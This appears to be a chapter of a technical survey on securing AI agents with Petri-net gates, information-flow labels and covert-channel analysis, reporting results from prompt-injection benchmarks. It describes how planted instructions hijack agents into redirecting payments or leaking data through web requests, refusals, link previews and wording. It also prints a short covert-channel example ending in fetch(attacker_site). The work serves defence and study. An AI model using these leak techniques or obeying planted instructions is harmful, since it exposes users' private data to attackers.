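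Gu and Zhu tested the admission rule with a script in place of a language model. The script proposed the correct next step most of the time, sometimes proposed a step too early, and in up to half of its proposals followed an injected order to deploy. Without a gate, or with a simulated classifier that missed 10% or 30% of injected orders, some deployments went ahead without approval. About 15% did so even with no injection, because the classifier is not designed to block a request that comes too early but was not injected. With the net, no deployment went ahead without approval in 10,000 runs at each setting. This result follows from the design, since the transition is not enabled without an approval. The script also never gave up after a refusal, so the test is little evidence of how a real agent would cope with refusals.

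### What refusals cost

In ordinary control theory, an event that the supervisor forbids doesn't happen. But when a gate refuses an AI agent's action, the agent gets an error message and tries again, and each attempt requires another call to the model. A hijacked agent may request the same forbidden action repeatedly.

Gu and Zhu show that the most permissive supervisor can be an expensive choice here. To adapt their example, suppose an agent can answer a letter immediately, or open the customer's record first and then answer. At the start it proposes to open the record with probability `a`. With the record open, it proposes a forbidden web search with probability `b`, and otherwise it answers. The expected number of model calls is

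```
gate allows opening the record:     1 + a / (1 − b)
gate refuses to open the record:    1 / (1 − a)
```

With `a` = 0.5 and `b` = 0.99, the permissive gate needs 51 calls on average and the stricter one needs two. Opening the record is safe, but it leads to a state in which the agent keeps making requests that the gate must refuse. As `b` approaches 1, the ratio between the two averages grows without limit.

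Gu and Zhu therefore refine the most permissive supervisor, using estimates of how often the agent proposes each action. The refined version also refuses an action if admitting it would lead to more expected further calls than refusing it. It only removes permissions, so it remains safe if the estimates are wrong, though it can then waste calls. If the true probabilities in the example were 0.99 and 0.01, a gate designed for the figures above would need 100 calls, while the permissive gate would need two.

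Good estimates will be hard to get because the calculation assumes that an agent's proposals depend only on the current marking. A real agent also reads the error message and may change its plan or abandon the task. Ray makes a similar point about tuning gates in general, that records of an agent working without a gate may not show how it will behave with one.

### What refusals reveal

A gate's error messages can also leak information. Suppose a gate refuses an agent's request for a customer's record. If the message is "access denied" when the customer exists and "no such customer" otherwise, the agent learns whether the person is a customer. It can then include that fact in a later call that the gate permits.

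*Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes this pattern and explains why common defences miss it. Many of them track the data that tools return, but a refused call returns no data. Chinaei's defence records each refusal as an event and links the agent's next tool call to it, so that a rule can stop the agent from sending data outside when that call may depend on a refusal. The link is a cautious guess, since nobody can see whether the refusal influenced the model. It may still miss some dependencies, because a refusal can influence calls long after the next one.

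In the clean and exposed net, the simplest fix is to treat any refusal that depends on secret data as a read. The agent then becomes exposed when it receives the error message. Alternatively, the gate can give the same answer in both cases.

Refusals can also carry information between agents, which is easy to overlook when using monitor places. Suppose all agents share a budget of 100 tool calls a day. High lookups and low web requests both take marks from the budget, so it is a conflict place. A hijacked records agent can use up some of the marks, and the observer can count how many requests the web agent still makes. If the web agent always uses whatever remains, the count has 101 possible values and can carry almost 6.7 bits a day. Gu and Zhu's safety theorem does not rule out this channel, because every run stays within the budget. Separate budgets for high and low actions close the channel.

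### Checking where a value came from

A gate that tracks only the order of actions cannot distinguish a payment to the right account from the same payment to an attacker's. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) therefore uses a coloured net that also checks the arguments of each call. The net has one kind of place that records the stage of the task, one that holds permissions, and one that collects tool results as evidence.

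A permission names a tool, limits how often the agent may use it, and says where each argument must come from. There are three options:

- The value must match one in the user's request or in a trusted record.
- It must come from a named field in the output of a named tool during the same session.
- The agent may choose it freely.

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay $100 to BillPay. The net receives a permission for one payment of this amount to this recipient. The agent then reads a tool result containing an instruction to pay Mallory instead. The agent proposes that payment, and the gate refuses because the recipient doesn't match the permission. The name Mallory is now in the evidence place, but evidence can never create a permission. The gate also reserves the permission before it executes a payment, so two simultaneous proposals cannot both use the same permission.

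The gate is ordinary software, but a language model writes its rules by turning the user's request into permissions before the agent starts. The model's only inputs are the request and trusted descriptions of the tools, so a malicious web page cannot reach it. If the agent later needs another permission, a separate judge model can grant it, which extends the Petri net. The net enforces the permissions exactly, but there is no proof that they are the right ones.

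Li and colleagues tested ToolFence on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do office, messaging, travel and banking tasks while attackers plant instructions in the data they read. It combines 97 user tasks and 27 attack goals into 629 test cases. In 524 of them, the attack needs a tool that the user's task does not, and in 85 it only changes the arguments of tools the task needs anyway. Li and colleagues left the other 20 unclassified. They also used three further benchmarks. With the model Qwen3-max as the agent, the results were:

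| Benchmark and attack | Successful attacks, no defence | Successful attacks, ToolFence | Tasks completed without attacks, before and after |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: planted instructions | 21.2% | 0.0% | 66.3% → 64.3% |
| ASB: planted instructions and false memories | 40.2% | 4.2% | 71.5% → 67.2% |
| MCPTox: malicious tool descriptions | 38.1% | 6.1% | 67.2% → 65.4% |
| AgentLAB: attacks spread over many records | 76.3% | 29.4% | 62.4% → 61.1% |

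On 200 AgentDojo cases, ToolFence took 1.63 times as long as the undefended agent. CaMeL, a defence that runs the agent's plan in a special interpreter, took 12.95 times as long. It stopped every attack on AgentDojo but completed only 43.1% of the ordinary tasks.

The zero on AgentDojo is a good result against known attacks, but it does not guarantee security. Those attacks followed six standard patterns and were not designed to mislead ToolFence's judge. AgentLAB is a harder test because its attackers spread their instructions over several records until the malicious step looks like a necessary part of the task, and the judge sometimes grants permission for it.

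The fixed checks provide most of the security, and the judge mainly keeps the agent useful. On ASB, with Llama3.3-70B as the agent, attacks succeeded in 5.1% of cases against the full system. Removing the checks on arguments raised that figure to 24.0%. Removing the judge left it nearly unchanged at 4.8%, but reduced the share of tasks the agent completed under attack from 44.3% to 35.8%.

In a banking task, the user's own request gave the attacker's account number as that of a new landlord, and the gate accepted the number because it came from a trusted source. This kind of failure would matter a great deal in the support deployment, where requests come from customers and an attacker can send one by writing a letter. If ToolFence treated the letter as the user's request, it would treat the addresses and account numbers in it as authorised.

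Another gap involves free arguments, which are those the agent may choose itself. A language model also classifies each argument as sensitive or free. If it classifies the text of a web search as free, the gate will accept a search that contains a customer's phone number. ToolFence checks whether a value has the right source for its role in the call, but it has no rule about where a customer's data may go.

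## Labels that travel with the data

Information-flow control provides the rule that ToolFence lacks. Software attaches a label to every value. The label records who may read the value and how much the system trusts it, and a gate checks the labels at every tool call. Dorothy Denning developed the theory for ordinary programs in 1976, and since 2025 several groups have applied it to AI agents.

### Two labels and one rule

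The simplest label has two parts. Confidentiality is either public or secret, and integrity is either trusted or untrusted. When a value depends on several others, its confidentiality rises to the highest of theirs and its integrity falls to the lowest. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, a defence unrelated to the Security Process Algebra, write the rule as

```
(c1, i1) ⊔ (c2, i2)  =  (c1 ⊔ c2, i1 ⊓ i2)
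```

Here `c1 ⊔ c2` is the lowest confidentiality level that is at least as high as both, and `i1 ⊓ i2` is the highest integrity level that is no higher than either. A set of levels is a lattice if any two of them have both kinds of bound. A value may go to a tool if it is no more confidential than the tool may receive and at least as trusted as the tool requires.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) explain in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that a confidentiality label can also be a set of permitted readers. When two values are combined, only readers in both sets may read the result. If staff and customer 1 may read one record, and staff and customer 2 may read another, only staff may read a text based on both. So if the mail agent uses both records in a reply, the gate can refuse to send it to either customer.

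### One record in three messages

Suppose the gate keeps a label for each agent, combining the labels of everything the agent has read. `fetch` accepts only public data, and `mail` accepts secret or untrusted text only if a person has approved it. The web agent has read a page about the error code, so its label is public and untrusted. The records agent then looks up a customer, and its label becomes secret and trusted.

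| Event | Label | Gate |
|---|---|---|
| Records agent sends a query with only the error code | secret, trusted | admits, since it stays inside |
| Web agent proposes to fetch a page for that code | secret, untrusted | refuses |
| Web agent sends findings from the page it read earlier | secret, untrusted | admits |
| Records agent sends a draft | secret, untrusted | admits |
| Mail agent proposes to send the reply | secret, untrusted | refuses without approval |

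The query contains no customer data, and the findings come from a public page, but both are labeled secret. In an ordinary program, `total = price + tax` makes `total` depend only on `price` and `tax`. But anything in a language model's context may affect anything it writes, so its output gets the most restrictive combination of the labels in that context.

Nothing the agent does later makes its label less restrictive. If a step fails and the agent tries again, the error message also enters its context. In a team, each message passes the sender's restrictions on to the receiver. After three messages, all three agents here are labeled secret and untrusted, and the team can't send anything without a person's approval. The net with clean and exposed places, which had the same problem, is the special case in which each agent has a single two-valued label.

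### A planner that never reads the page

Willison proposed splitting the work between two models. A planner reads the user's request and decides which tools to call, but never sees untrusted text. A second model, which has no tools, reads that text and can only return values. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes this as a way to keep untrusted data from tainting the planner's context.

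CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, adds labels to this arrangement. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, the planner turns the request into a short program in restricted Python. An interpreter runs the program, calls the tools and stores each result in a variable, along with a record of its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, a policy function checks the arguments and their records, then allows or denies the call. A malicious page can change a variable's value but cannot add a step to the program.

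For the support deployment, a member of staff might type in a customer's name and an error code. The plan and its labels could then be

```
record = lookup(customer)         secret, trusted
page   = fetch(error_code)        public, untrusted
reply  = read(record, page)       secret, untrusted
mail(customer, reply)             needs approval
```

The gate allows the web request even though it comes after the lookup, because the address depends only on the error code. The clean and exposed net would have blocked it. Labelling values instead of agents is safe here because the planner chose this request before anyone opened the record. As with ToolFence, customers' letters cannot safely be used as requests.

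A fixed plan is awkward when the next step depends on the contents of a page. FIDES, the system of Costa and colleagues, therefore keeps the usual loop, in which the planner chooses one step at a time. If a tool result would make the planner's label more restrictive, the software stores the result in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass that name to another tool, and the software fills in the value just before the call.

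This is enough for "send this page to my colleague", but not for "do the tasks on today's list", because the planner needs information about the tasks. The planner can instead send a question about the hidden text to a second model that has no tools, and the software forces the answer into a fixed format. An attacker can do little with a yes-or-no answer, so a policy may treat it more leniently than free text. Each answer still carries one bit, however, and enough of them can reveal a whole phone number.

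### The branch that does not run

A label tracker can miss a secret that affects which steps run. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found that CaMeL's interpreter has this fault. Adapted to one bit of a phone number, their example is

```
tmp  = True
leak = True
if bit == 1:  tmp  = False
if tmp:       leak = False
if leak:      fetch(attacker_site)
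```

If the bit is 1, `tmp` becomes false and secret. The program skips the line that would change `leak`, so `leak` keeps its public label and the request goes out. If the bit is 0, `leak` becomes false and no request goes out. The attacker learns the bit from whether their site gets a request. CaMeL updates labels only on the branch that runs, so it has the weakness that Bijani found in step-by-step checks.

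A planner that has read only a benign request is unlikely to write this program, but the example shows that CaMeL's labels do not guarantee noninterference. CaMeL also retries failed plans in a loop outside the interpreter, where nothing tracks labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) partly blames Python, whose exceptions and dynamic types make programs hard to analyse, and recommends a small language designed for security.

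FIDES has a noninterference theorem for its own agent loop, but Garby and colleagues point out that its guarantee for secrets is weaker. That guarantee covers data that reaches a tool's arguments, but not implicit flows such as the recall notice request that Bijani's type checker rejected.

### Checking the plan before it runs

If the whole plan exists before any tool runs, software can check every branch. *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2025) has a model write the plan from the user's request alone, using imaginary tools such as "load document" and "summarise text". A second stage then matches these to installed tools, so a malicious tool description cannot influence the plan's structure. ACE compares the labels in the plan with what each tool may receive, and rejects the plan if, for example, a financial record would reach a mail tool that lacks clearance for it. The user has to label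 every source of information, and the check misses leaks from any source with the wrong label.

SPA uses a smaller language with six kinds of step. Every step inside an `if` or a loop inherits the label of the data that controls it. The recall notice request therefore becomes secret, and the check rejects the plan whether or not the customer owns the router. It also rejects a loop that makes one web request per past complaint. This language cannot express the program that CaMeL failed to catch, because a plan cannot reassign a variable, and variables set inside a branch disappear when the branch ends.

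SPA calls the planner once and gives it no feedback on why a plan failed, which avoids CaMeL's retry loop. The check uses only labels, so a rejection reveals nothing about secret values, provided the labels do not depend on those values. Girrens and Wang describe the checking algorithm but give no noninterference theorem for it.

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) checks each call just before it runs, using a graph of where data has travelled. One check looks for paths from protected or untrusted data to a harmful effect and tries to cut them. Another determines whether the user's request authorised that effect. Li, Wang and colleagues prove that cutting a path prevents the corresponding real leak if the graph represents every step of that leak. They state that this guarantee is not noninterference, and that an attacker could still learn something from a refusal.

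The theorem about PACE applies to a strict version, but the experiments used a version that can restore calls the path check has blocked. The reason is that the path check alone reduced completed tasks from 76.8% to 13.6% on a subset of AgentDojo.

### What the checks cost

These results come from different tests and models, so they do not rank the systems.

| System and test | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
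|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, AgentDojo banking tasks, rerun by Garby and colleagues with GPT-5.2 | 0 of 231 | 66.7% without policy checks, 37.5% with them |
| FIDES, AgentDojo | none, with suitable policies | 8% more than a basic agent under the same checks with GPT-4o, 16% more with o1 |
| ACE, InjecAgent | 0 of 1,054 | 75.2% |
| SPA, AgentDojo | 0 of 949 | 53.0% without label checks, 29.0% with them |
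| PACE as tested, AgentDojo, three models | 0%, 5.1% and 8.1% in the worst attack group | at most 3 points fewer than without a defence |

SPA's label checks added very little measured security. Without them, only 4 of the 949 attacks succeeded, because a page cannot change an existing plan. Adding the checks stopped those four attacks but nearly halved the number of completed tasks. About 53% of runs ended because the check rejected the plan, usually for passing untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted data. Many ordinary tasks need to do this, such as paying the amount on an invoice.

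Garby and colleagues found a similar pattern in AgentDojo's banking tasks. In 97 of the 144 task-attack combinations, the attack needs a tool call that the user's plan would never contain, so separating the planner generally defeats it without labels. Labels matter in the other 47, where the attack could succeed within the plan. The phone number in a web address is an attack of the second kind, so the benchmark totals probably understate how much the support deployment would gain from labels.

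No InjecAgent attack succeeded against ACE, for a similar reason. InjecAgent counts an attack as successful only if it triggers one of the attacker's tools, and ACE never puts a tool's output into the planner's context. The result is therefore weak evidence about ACE's label check. Planning with imaginary tools also depends heavily on matching them to installed ones. When Girrens and Wang tried it in SPA with a small model, about 75% of runs failed because no installed tool matched.

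Results from rerunning a rival's system call for some caution. Garby and colleagues saw no successful attack on CaMeL with its policy checks on, while Li, Wang and colleagues report success rates of up to 36% in the worst category of attacks. The two teams used different attacks, models and sets of tasks, and neither developed CaMeL.

### A calculus with a theorem

Garby and colleagues built LLMbda to give agents' labels a proper proof. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which every program consists of functions applied to values. The main additions are

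```
send e        add the value of e to the conversation as a prompt
recv          sample the model's response, parse it and run it
fork e        run e, then restore the conversation as it was
clear         empty the conversation
l : e         add the label l to the value of e
l ? e         test whether the value of e may flow to l
assert l e    stop the run unless it may
```

The usual call to a model, `@e`, is a `send` followed by a `recv`. The conversation has its own label, which combines the labels of all the prompts sent. Any code in a response runs under that label. A program can build Willison's second model by forking the conversation, clearing the copy, and asking the copy about the untrusted page. The answer comes back with an untrusted label, but the main conversation's label doesn't change.

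LLMbda stops the run if the program tries to add a message to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret. Otherwise, the conversation would be secret on one run and public on another, and the public one would reveal which branch the program took.

The theorem compares two starting points that look the same to an observer at some level. A model answers at random, so each gives a probability for every outcome the observer can see, and the missing probability is the chance that the run never finishes. The theorem states that the two distributions, `μ` and `ν`, are compatible, which means that some `ω` satisfies

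```
μ(q) ≤ ω(q)  and  ν(q) ≤ ω(q)  for every outcome q,
and the sum of all ω(q) is at most 1
```

The agent that sent the correct bit with probability 0.95 has incompatible distributions for a 0 and a 1, because `ω` would need to be at least 0.95 on each outcome, a total of 1.9. If runs always finish, compatible distributions must be equal, as in probabilistic noninterference. If runs sometimes stall, the distance between compatible distributions is at most the average probability of stalling. For example, an agent passes if it answers "ok" with probability 0.9 for one secret and 0.6 for another, and otherwise stalls.

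The proof replaces every computation that becomes secret with a dummy value. The simplified program behaves identically for both secrets and finishes at least as often as the original, so its distribution can serve as `ω`. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean and proved that their interpreter follows the calculus. The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during the run, and holds however well or badly the model behaves.

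It assumes that developers label the sources correctly and put checks on the sensitive tools. It also requires that a model's response depend only on the conversation and chance, and that all tools and data sources be part of the program. The calculus runs one step at a time, so it has no agents working in parallel.

Programs can override integrity labels with an `endorse` step, for instance after reducing an email to one of a few fixed categories. The theorem still guarantees that secrets are protected after this step, but not that the endorsed data is trustworthy. In tests on AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in LLMbda completed 36 of 48 runs with GPT-5.2, about as many as CaMeL did without its policy checks. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file.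 Without endorsement, the agent resists this attack but also cannot do the task when the file is genuine.

### Labels beside processes and nets

Labels handle values more easily than process and net models do, because a program that checks those models needs a short list of possible values, while a label can cover text of any length. But labels don't measure how much of a secret a value contains, so a query with only an error code is treated the same as one with a phone number.

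Nets handle order and counting better than labels do. The label on an approved reply would let the mail agent send it twice, whereas a net can use up the approval mark on the first mail. A label system needs a separate counter, such as the budgets that PACE attaches to permissions. However, labels can show that a count depends on a secret, as SPA's rule for loops does.

Labels are weakest against blocking between concurrent agents. As in the clean and exposed net, a hijacked records agent can signal by choosing which web agents to block. BNDC detects this, but a label check does not, because each refusal is correct.

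LLMbda's theorem also permits secrets to affect whether a run finishes, which matters more when an outsider can watch the run. Suppose a program sends numbered web requests and stalls when the number equals a customer's four-digit PIN. The run never finishes, so it has no outcome to compare and the theorem doesn't cover it, but the website's owner can read the PIN from the last request. SPA's interpreter stops on any error, so an error in a step that handles secret data can likewise prevent a later public request.

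### Systems for several agents

*SAFEFLOW* (Li, Zou and colleagues, 2025) gives each user, agent, environment and piece of data a single number. A lower number means both more trusted and more sensitive. An agent may act on data with the same number as its own. It may read but not act on data with a higher number, and it may not read data with a lower one. A single number cannot describe a customer's letter, which is both private and untrusted. A language model acting as a verifier can change these numbers, so the protection depends partly on its judgement.

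SAFEFLOW mainly offers measurements. In 332 scenarios with deceptive screens and pages, ten models took unsafe actions in 56% to 79% of cases without SAFEFLOW and in none with it. In 25 further scenarios, where two to five agents competed for shared resources, GPT-4.1 completed one without SAFEFLOW and all 25 with it. These 25 scenarios test coordination, not secrecy. SAFEFLOW coordinates agents with locks, which let one agent delay another. In a Petri net, such a lock is the kind of conflict place that can leak information.

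*AgentSafe* (Mao, Meng and colleagues, 2025) gives each agent a permission level and divides its memory into layers, so that an agent may read only information at its own level or below. An agent may also send messages only to agents at its own level or below. In the support deployment, the records agent could then send queries to a less privileged web agent, but the web agent could not send its findings back. The messaging rule keeps untrusted agents from influencing trusted ones, but keeping the query secret depends on giving it the right level.

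The evidence for AgentSafe also consists of measured defence rates, from tests with six agents and an attacker. Against attacks that confuse agents about who has authority, the defence rate with AgentSafe was 86% after 5 turns and 83% after 50, compared with 50% and 55% without it. Against attackers who impersonated other agents, the rate with AgentSafe fell from 77% after 5 turns to 46% after 50.

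## Channels the model leaves out and the cost of a fuller one

Like every check so far, AgentSafe's rules apply only to listed channels, so they miss unlisted ones such as the shared disk. Jaskolka (2015), in *On the Modelling, Analysis, and Mitigation of Distributed Covert Channels*, traces the term "covert channel" to Butler Lampson, who in 1973 defined it as a channel that nobody designed or intended to carry information.

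### Which agents can reach which

Jaskolka and Khedri (2014), in *A Formulation of the Potential for Communication Condition using C2KA*, set out an algebra for finding agents that could use such a channel. Like a process algebra, it builds behaviours from choice, sequence, parallel composition and repetition. But where a CCS message goes to one partner that is ready for it, here an agent emits a stimulus that reaches every other agent. Two functions describe what happens:

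```
s ∘ a      the behaviour of an agent a after stimulus s
λ(s, a)    the stimulus that a emits in response to s
```

An agent `a` can influence an agent `b` directly in two ways:

```
by stimulus:      for some s, λ(s, a) includes a basic stimulus t with  t ∘ b ≠ b
by environment:   a R b,  where R lists which behaviours depend on which
```

If a chain of these links leads from one agent to another, the two agents have the "potential for communication". The shared disk is a link of the second kind, because the web agent's behaviour depends on how much space the records agent has left.

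The algebra also shows the effect of replacing an agent in the middle of a chain. A replacement that does nothing breaks the chain, and one that ignores all stimuli can keep it intact only through the shared environment. Adding a slow step to an agent may leave the chain intact but disturb a channel that relies on timing.

Jaskolka and Khedri assume that `R` is given. They suggest building it with an older technique, the Shared Resource Matrix, in which an analyst checks whether one agent could signal to another through each shared resource. The analyst can therefore use the algebra to work out the consequences of a shared disk only after someone has identified the disk as a shared resource.

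The algebra also raises false alarms. Suppose the mailbox between the web agent and the records agent acknowledges each delivery. The records agent changes the mailbox by emptying it, and the mailbox changes the web agent by acknowledging its findings, so a chain leads from the records agent to the web agent. But the mailbox satisfies BNDC, because it sends the acknowledgement whether it was full or empty. The algebra is most useful as a quick first pass to find the pairs of agents worth checking with BNDC.

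### Six kinds of channel

Agent deployments add at least six kinds of channel to the messages in our model. A process or a net can represent most of them:

| Channel | What the modeller adds | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Automatic web requests | A process for the program that makes them | A few states |
| Tool arguments | A variable for each argument | A copy of the action for each class of content |
| Shared memory and files | A process or place for each shared item | A state for each class of content or amount of free space |
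| Timing | An action `tick` that all components take together | A state for each tick a component may wait |
| Error messages | A separate action for each error an agent can tell apart | Extra branches at every call |
| Choice of wording | An action for each text an observer can tell apart | Too many to list |

Automatic requests are cheap to model but easy to forget. In an example from Willison (2024), a chatbot posts a link and the chat application loads the page to show a preview. The application makes the request, so a gate on the agent's tools never receives it. One line is enough to model this:

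```
Chat = post?(x).preview!(x).Chat
```

Treating `preview` as a low action in the model reveals that anything in a posted link can reach the website. Developers of apps that post to Slack can turn these previews off, but only if they know the previews exist.

Shared storage need not leak information, even if its space is limited. Bossi and colleagues model a buffer that a low producer fills and a high consumer empties. When the buffer is full, it still accepts new items but discards them, so the producer cannot tell how many items the consumer has taken. The drawback is that some items are lost without warning.

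Changing the system may be easier than modeling its timing. *AgenticOS* (2026), a design for an agent operating system, sends external requests in batches at fixed times and pads outputs to fixed sizes. It also lists the decision whether to make a call as a channel. It concedes that covert channels "cannot be completely eliminated" and aims to make them slow enough to monitor.

A single `error` action is too coarse to model error messages, because an agent that learns "disk full" knows more than one that learns only that something failed. Refusals by a gate raise the same problem.

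Wording is the hardest channel to model. In *Despite Instructions* (2026), some pairs of agents learned to pass on hidden findings through the wording of ordinary messages, without agreeing on a code beforehand. Nobody can list every such code, so the safe approach, which the label systems take, is to treat all free text as secret if the agent that wrote it has read a secret.

### How often data takes these routes

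Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured how often an audit of an agent's answers would miss an attack. A user asked the agent to summarise a web page, and the software automatically loaded a preview containing a planted instruction to send private data elsewhere. At least one request reached the receiving server in 423 of 480 runs (88%), compared with none in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's answer gave no sign of the attack.

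Even when the model was told never to follow instructions from web content, 20 of 30 attacks succeeded. A list of permitted domains stopped all 30, although the agent attempted a request every time. In process algebra, such a list is a restriction on `fetch`, and the restriction works whatever the agent tries to do. But this was an easy case for the defence, because the attacker's domain was clearly not on the list. In other ways the set-up favoured the attacker, with one small model, a minimal prompt and the private data in plain view.

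Agents also leak data without an attacker. *AgentRaft* (Lin, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested five existing agents with the same language model and tools. Each task required an agent to read private data with one tool and send certain fields to a third party with another. The researchers tried each path with five prompts and counted it as over-sharing if the agent sent an unnecessary field in any run. This happened in 759 of 2,337 tests (32%). In the affected runs, 80% of the fields sent were unnecessary. A model based on the intended task would contain `mail!(date)` even though the real agent may perform `mail!(record)`.

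The software around the model made a large difference to over-sharing. Claude Code over-shared in 12% of runs and Codex in 34%, although both used the same language model. Three language models voted on which fields were necessary, and the results closely matched human annotators' judgments on a sample.

*ContextLeak* (Jia, Wang and colleagues, 2026) studied malicious tools whose names and descriptions encourage an agent to pass them its context, such as the user's request or the conversation so far. In the main test, with 200 simulated users, agents chose the malicious tool in 86% to 92% of cases, depending on the type of context it targeted. For six other language models, the range was 56% to 85%. Claude Code chose the malicious tool in 22 of 100 cases, and then passed on text very close in meaning to the targeted context. Four detectors missed 97% to 100% of the malicious tools. All these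 figures assume that the user has already installed the tool. A formal model should therefore not assume that a tool's stated purpose limits what its arguments contain.

Inside a deployment, unnecessary sharing is even more common. In *AgentLeak*, El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah (2026) analysed 4,979 runs with five older models. Data that the task did not require appeared in the final output in 27% of runs, in shared memory in 47% and in messages between agents in 69%. An audit of final outputs alone would have missed such data in 42% of all runs, or about 61% of the runs where it appeared. Our outside observer would not see the internal messages, so these are not yet leaks in our sense. But they give more agents access to the data, and any of those agents may be able to send it out.

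### The size of a fuller model

Ten agents with 20 states each have 20^10, or about 10^13, joint states, even if the model leaves out message content. Some of these states may be unreachable, but storing eight bytes for every one would take about 82 terabytes. If each agent also has to remember one bit, the number of joint states rises to about 10^16.

Testing equivalence takes far longer than listing the states. For a system with `n` states, Bossi and colleagues give a time bound with a term that grows as `n` to the power 2.376, the exponent of the fastest matrix multiplication algorithm known at the time. For 10^13 states, this term comes to about 10^31 steps, so the check is impractical at this size even though it takes polynomial time.

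Even if modellers classify messages only as public or secret, each mailbox can be empty, hold a public message or hold a secret one. Ten mailboxes therefore multiply the number of states by 3 to the power 10, or about 59,000.

Classes that are too coarse can also hide leaks. Suppose the records agent asks the web agent to look up manufacturer A for customers who have complained before and manufacturer B for everyone else. Both names are public, so the model represents both lookups as the same action, `fetch_public`, and shows no leak. But the observer sees which name the web agent looked up and learns whether the customer has complained before.

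The modeller can fix this by giving the two names separate actions, which makes the model larger. Alternatively, the class can depend on what a message's author has read, as in the label systems. This keeps the model small and safe but also rejects harmless queries.

### Checking one component at a time

If we could check the ten agents separately, we would have 200 states to examine instead of 10^13. This works only if a property of the parts is also a property of the whole, which is not true of BNDC. `Flaky`, the status mail that sometimes fails for internal reasons, satisfies BNDC. So does `Timer`, which fetches a page and then ends the maintenance job:

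```
Flaky = τ.mail! + τ.0 + begin?.end?.mail!
Timer = fetch!.end!
```

Here `begin` and `end` are high. When `Flaky` and `Timer` run in parallel, an attacker can begin the job, and `Flaky` then waits for `end`, which `Timer` offers only after fetching its page. In the resulting state, the mail cannot go out before the web request but can always go out after it. The pair never reaches such a state without the attacker, so the pair fails BNDC.

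On its own, `Flaky` is secure because waiting for `end` looks like an ordinary failure to send. `Timer` makes the difference visible by ending the wait after an action the observer can see. Persistent BNDC prevents this problem by rejecting `Flaky` before anyone combines it with another process.

Bossi and colleagues compare three stricter versions of BNDC. Each requires that whenever a high step is possible, the system can reach a state that looks the same to a low observer without taking that step. The versions differ in how many internal steps the system takes to get there:

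| Property | Internal steps | In parallel | In a choice |
|---|---|---|---|
| BNDC | no such condition | can fail | can fail |
| Persistent BNDC | zero or more | preserved | can fail |
| Strong BNDC | none | preserved | can fail |
| Compositional persistent BNDC | one or more | preserved | preserved |

Choice can make a process insecure because a high step can remove a low option. A process that only looks up a record is secure, and so is one that only sends a mail. But `lookup! + mail!` is insecure, because after a lookup it can no longer send the mail. Adding the branch `τ.0` makes it secure again, since the process can then also lose that option through an internal step. The problem affects a single agent that has to choose between a secret job and a public one.

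Bossi and colleagues also describe a proof system that establishes persistent BNDC from the text of a process, without building its states. It works even for some processes with infinitely many states.

Shared resources count as components too. A disk with limited space violates all four properties if a high write can make a low write fail, so checking only the agents would miss the problem.

### Agents that join during a run

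Persistent BNDC also helps when a deployment changes. If the running system and a new component both satisfy it, the combined system does too, whatever state the running system is in when the component joins, so nobody needs to recheck the old components.

However, the decision to add a component must not depend on a secret. Suppose the records agent starts an extra web agent only for difficult cases:

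```
Start = spawn?.Watch
```

If `spawn` is high, `Start` fails BNDC because its web requests reveal that a difficult case has arrived. The pi-calculus can describe new processes and channels directly. In a Petri net, an added mark can represent another copy of a known agent, but a new kind of tool needs new transitions.

Changing how agents are connected also changes who receives data. Ogundoyin and Ikram (2026), in *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel*, ran 485 scenarios with different arrangements of agents and no attacker. The rate at which protected data reached newly introduced agents rose from 0% in the original two-agent arrangement, which had no newcomers, to as much as 52% in others. But the overall leakage rate stayed between 61% and 63%, so an auditor who tracked only that figure would have missed the change.

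Ogundoyin and Ikram also tested a filter that checks whether each recipient may have the data. It reduced unauthorised disclosure from 97% to 29% and kept 94% of the permitted disclosures. Removing all the sensitive data it detected gave almost the same protection, at 28%, but kept only 21% of the permitted disclosures. Nearly all the remaining leaks occurred because the detector failed to recognise the data. The logs recorded a recipient only for messages between agents and reads from shared memory, so for the other channels the modeller has to find out who can read the data.

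### Who writes the model

Perhaps no single person knows all the channels. A company's engineers know which agents they have connected, but they may not know that a supplier's chat application loads previews.

Software can produce a first draft. AgentRaft builds a graph of which tools can pass data to which by comparing their input and output types, then using a language model to check whether each connection makes sense. Lin and colleagues compared its graphs with ones that people had made for 233 tool functions. AgentRaft found 653 of the 720 real connections and added 42 that did not exist. Missing connections are the more serious errors for a security proof because they can make it worthless, while extra ones may cause false alarms. The graph also needs frequent rechecking if tools change while the system runs.

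Engineers can test a model by replaying recorded runs in it. If the system did something that the model cannot do, the model is wrong. The recordings should include network traffic as well as tool calls, because a web request that matches no tool call may come from an automatic preview. Engineers can also run the deployment twice, changing only the phone number, and compare what leaves the company.

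Replaying runs does not show that the system can do everything the model can. If the model is `Either`, which can send with or without a read, and the code is `Only`, which always reads first, every recorded run fits the model but the system still leaks. Small trusted components are easier to check. The mailbox has two states and three transitions, so engineers can test each transition and check that no others are possible. Agents with only high actions or only low ones need no such test, but engineers still have to check that these agents have no other actions.
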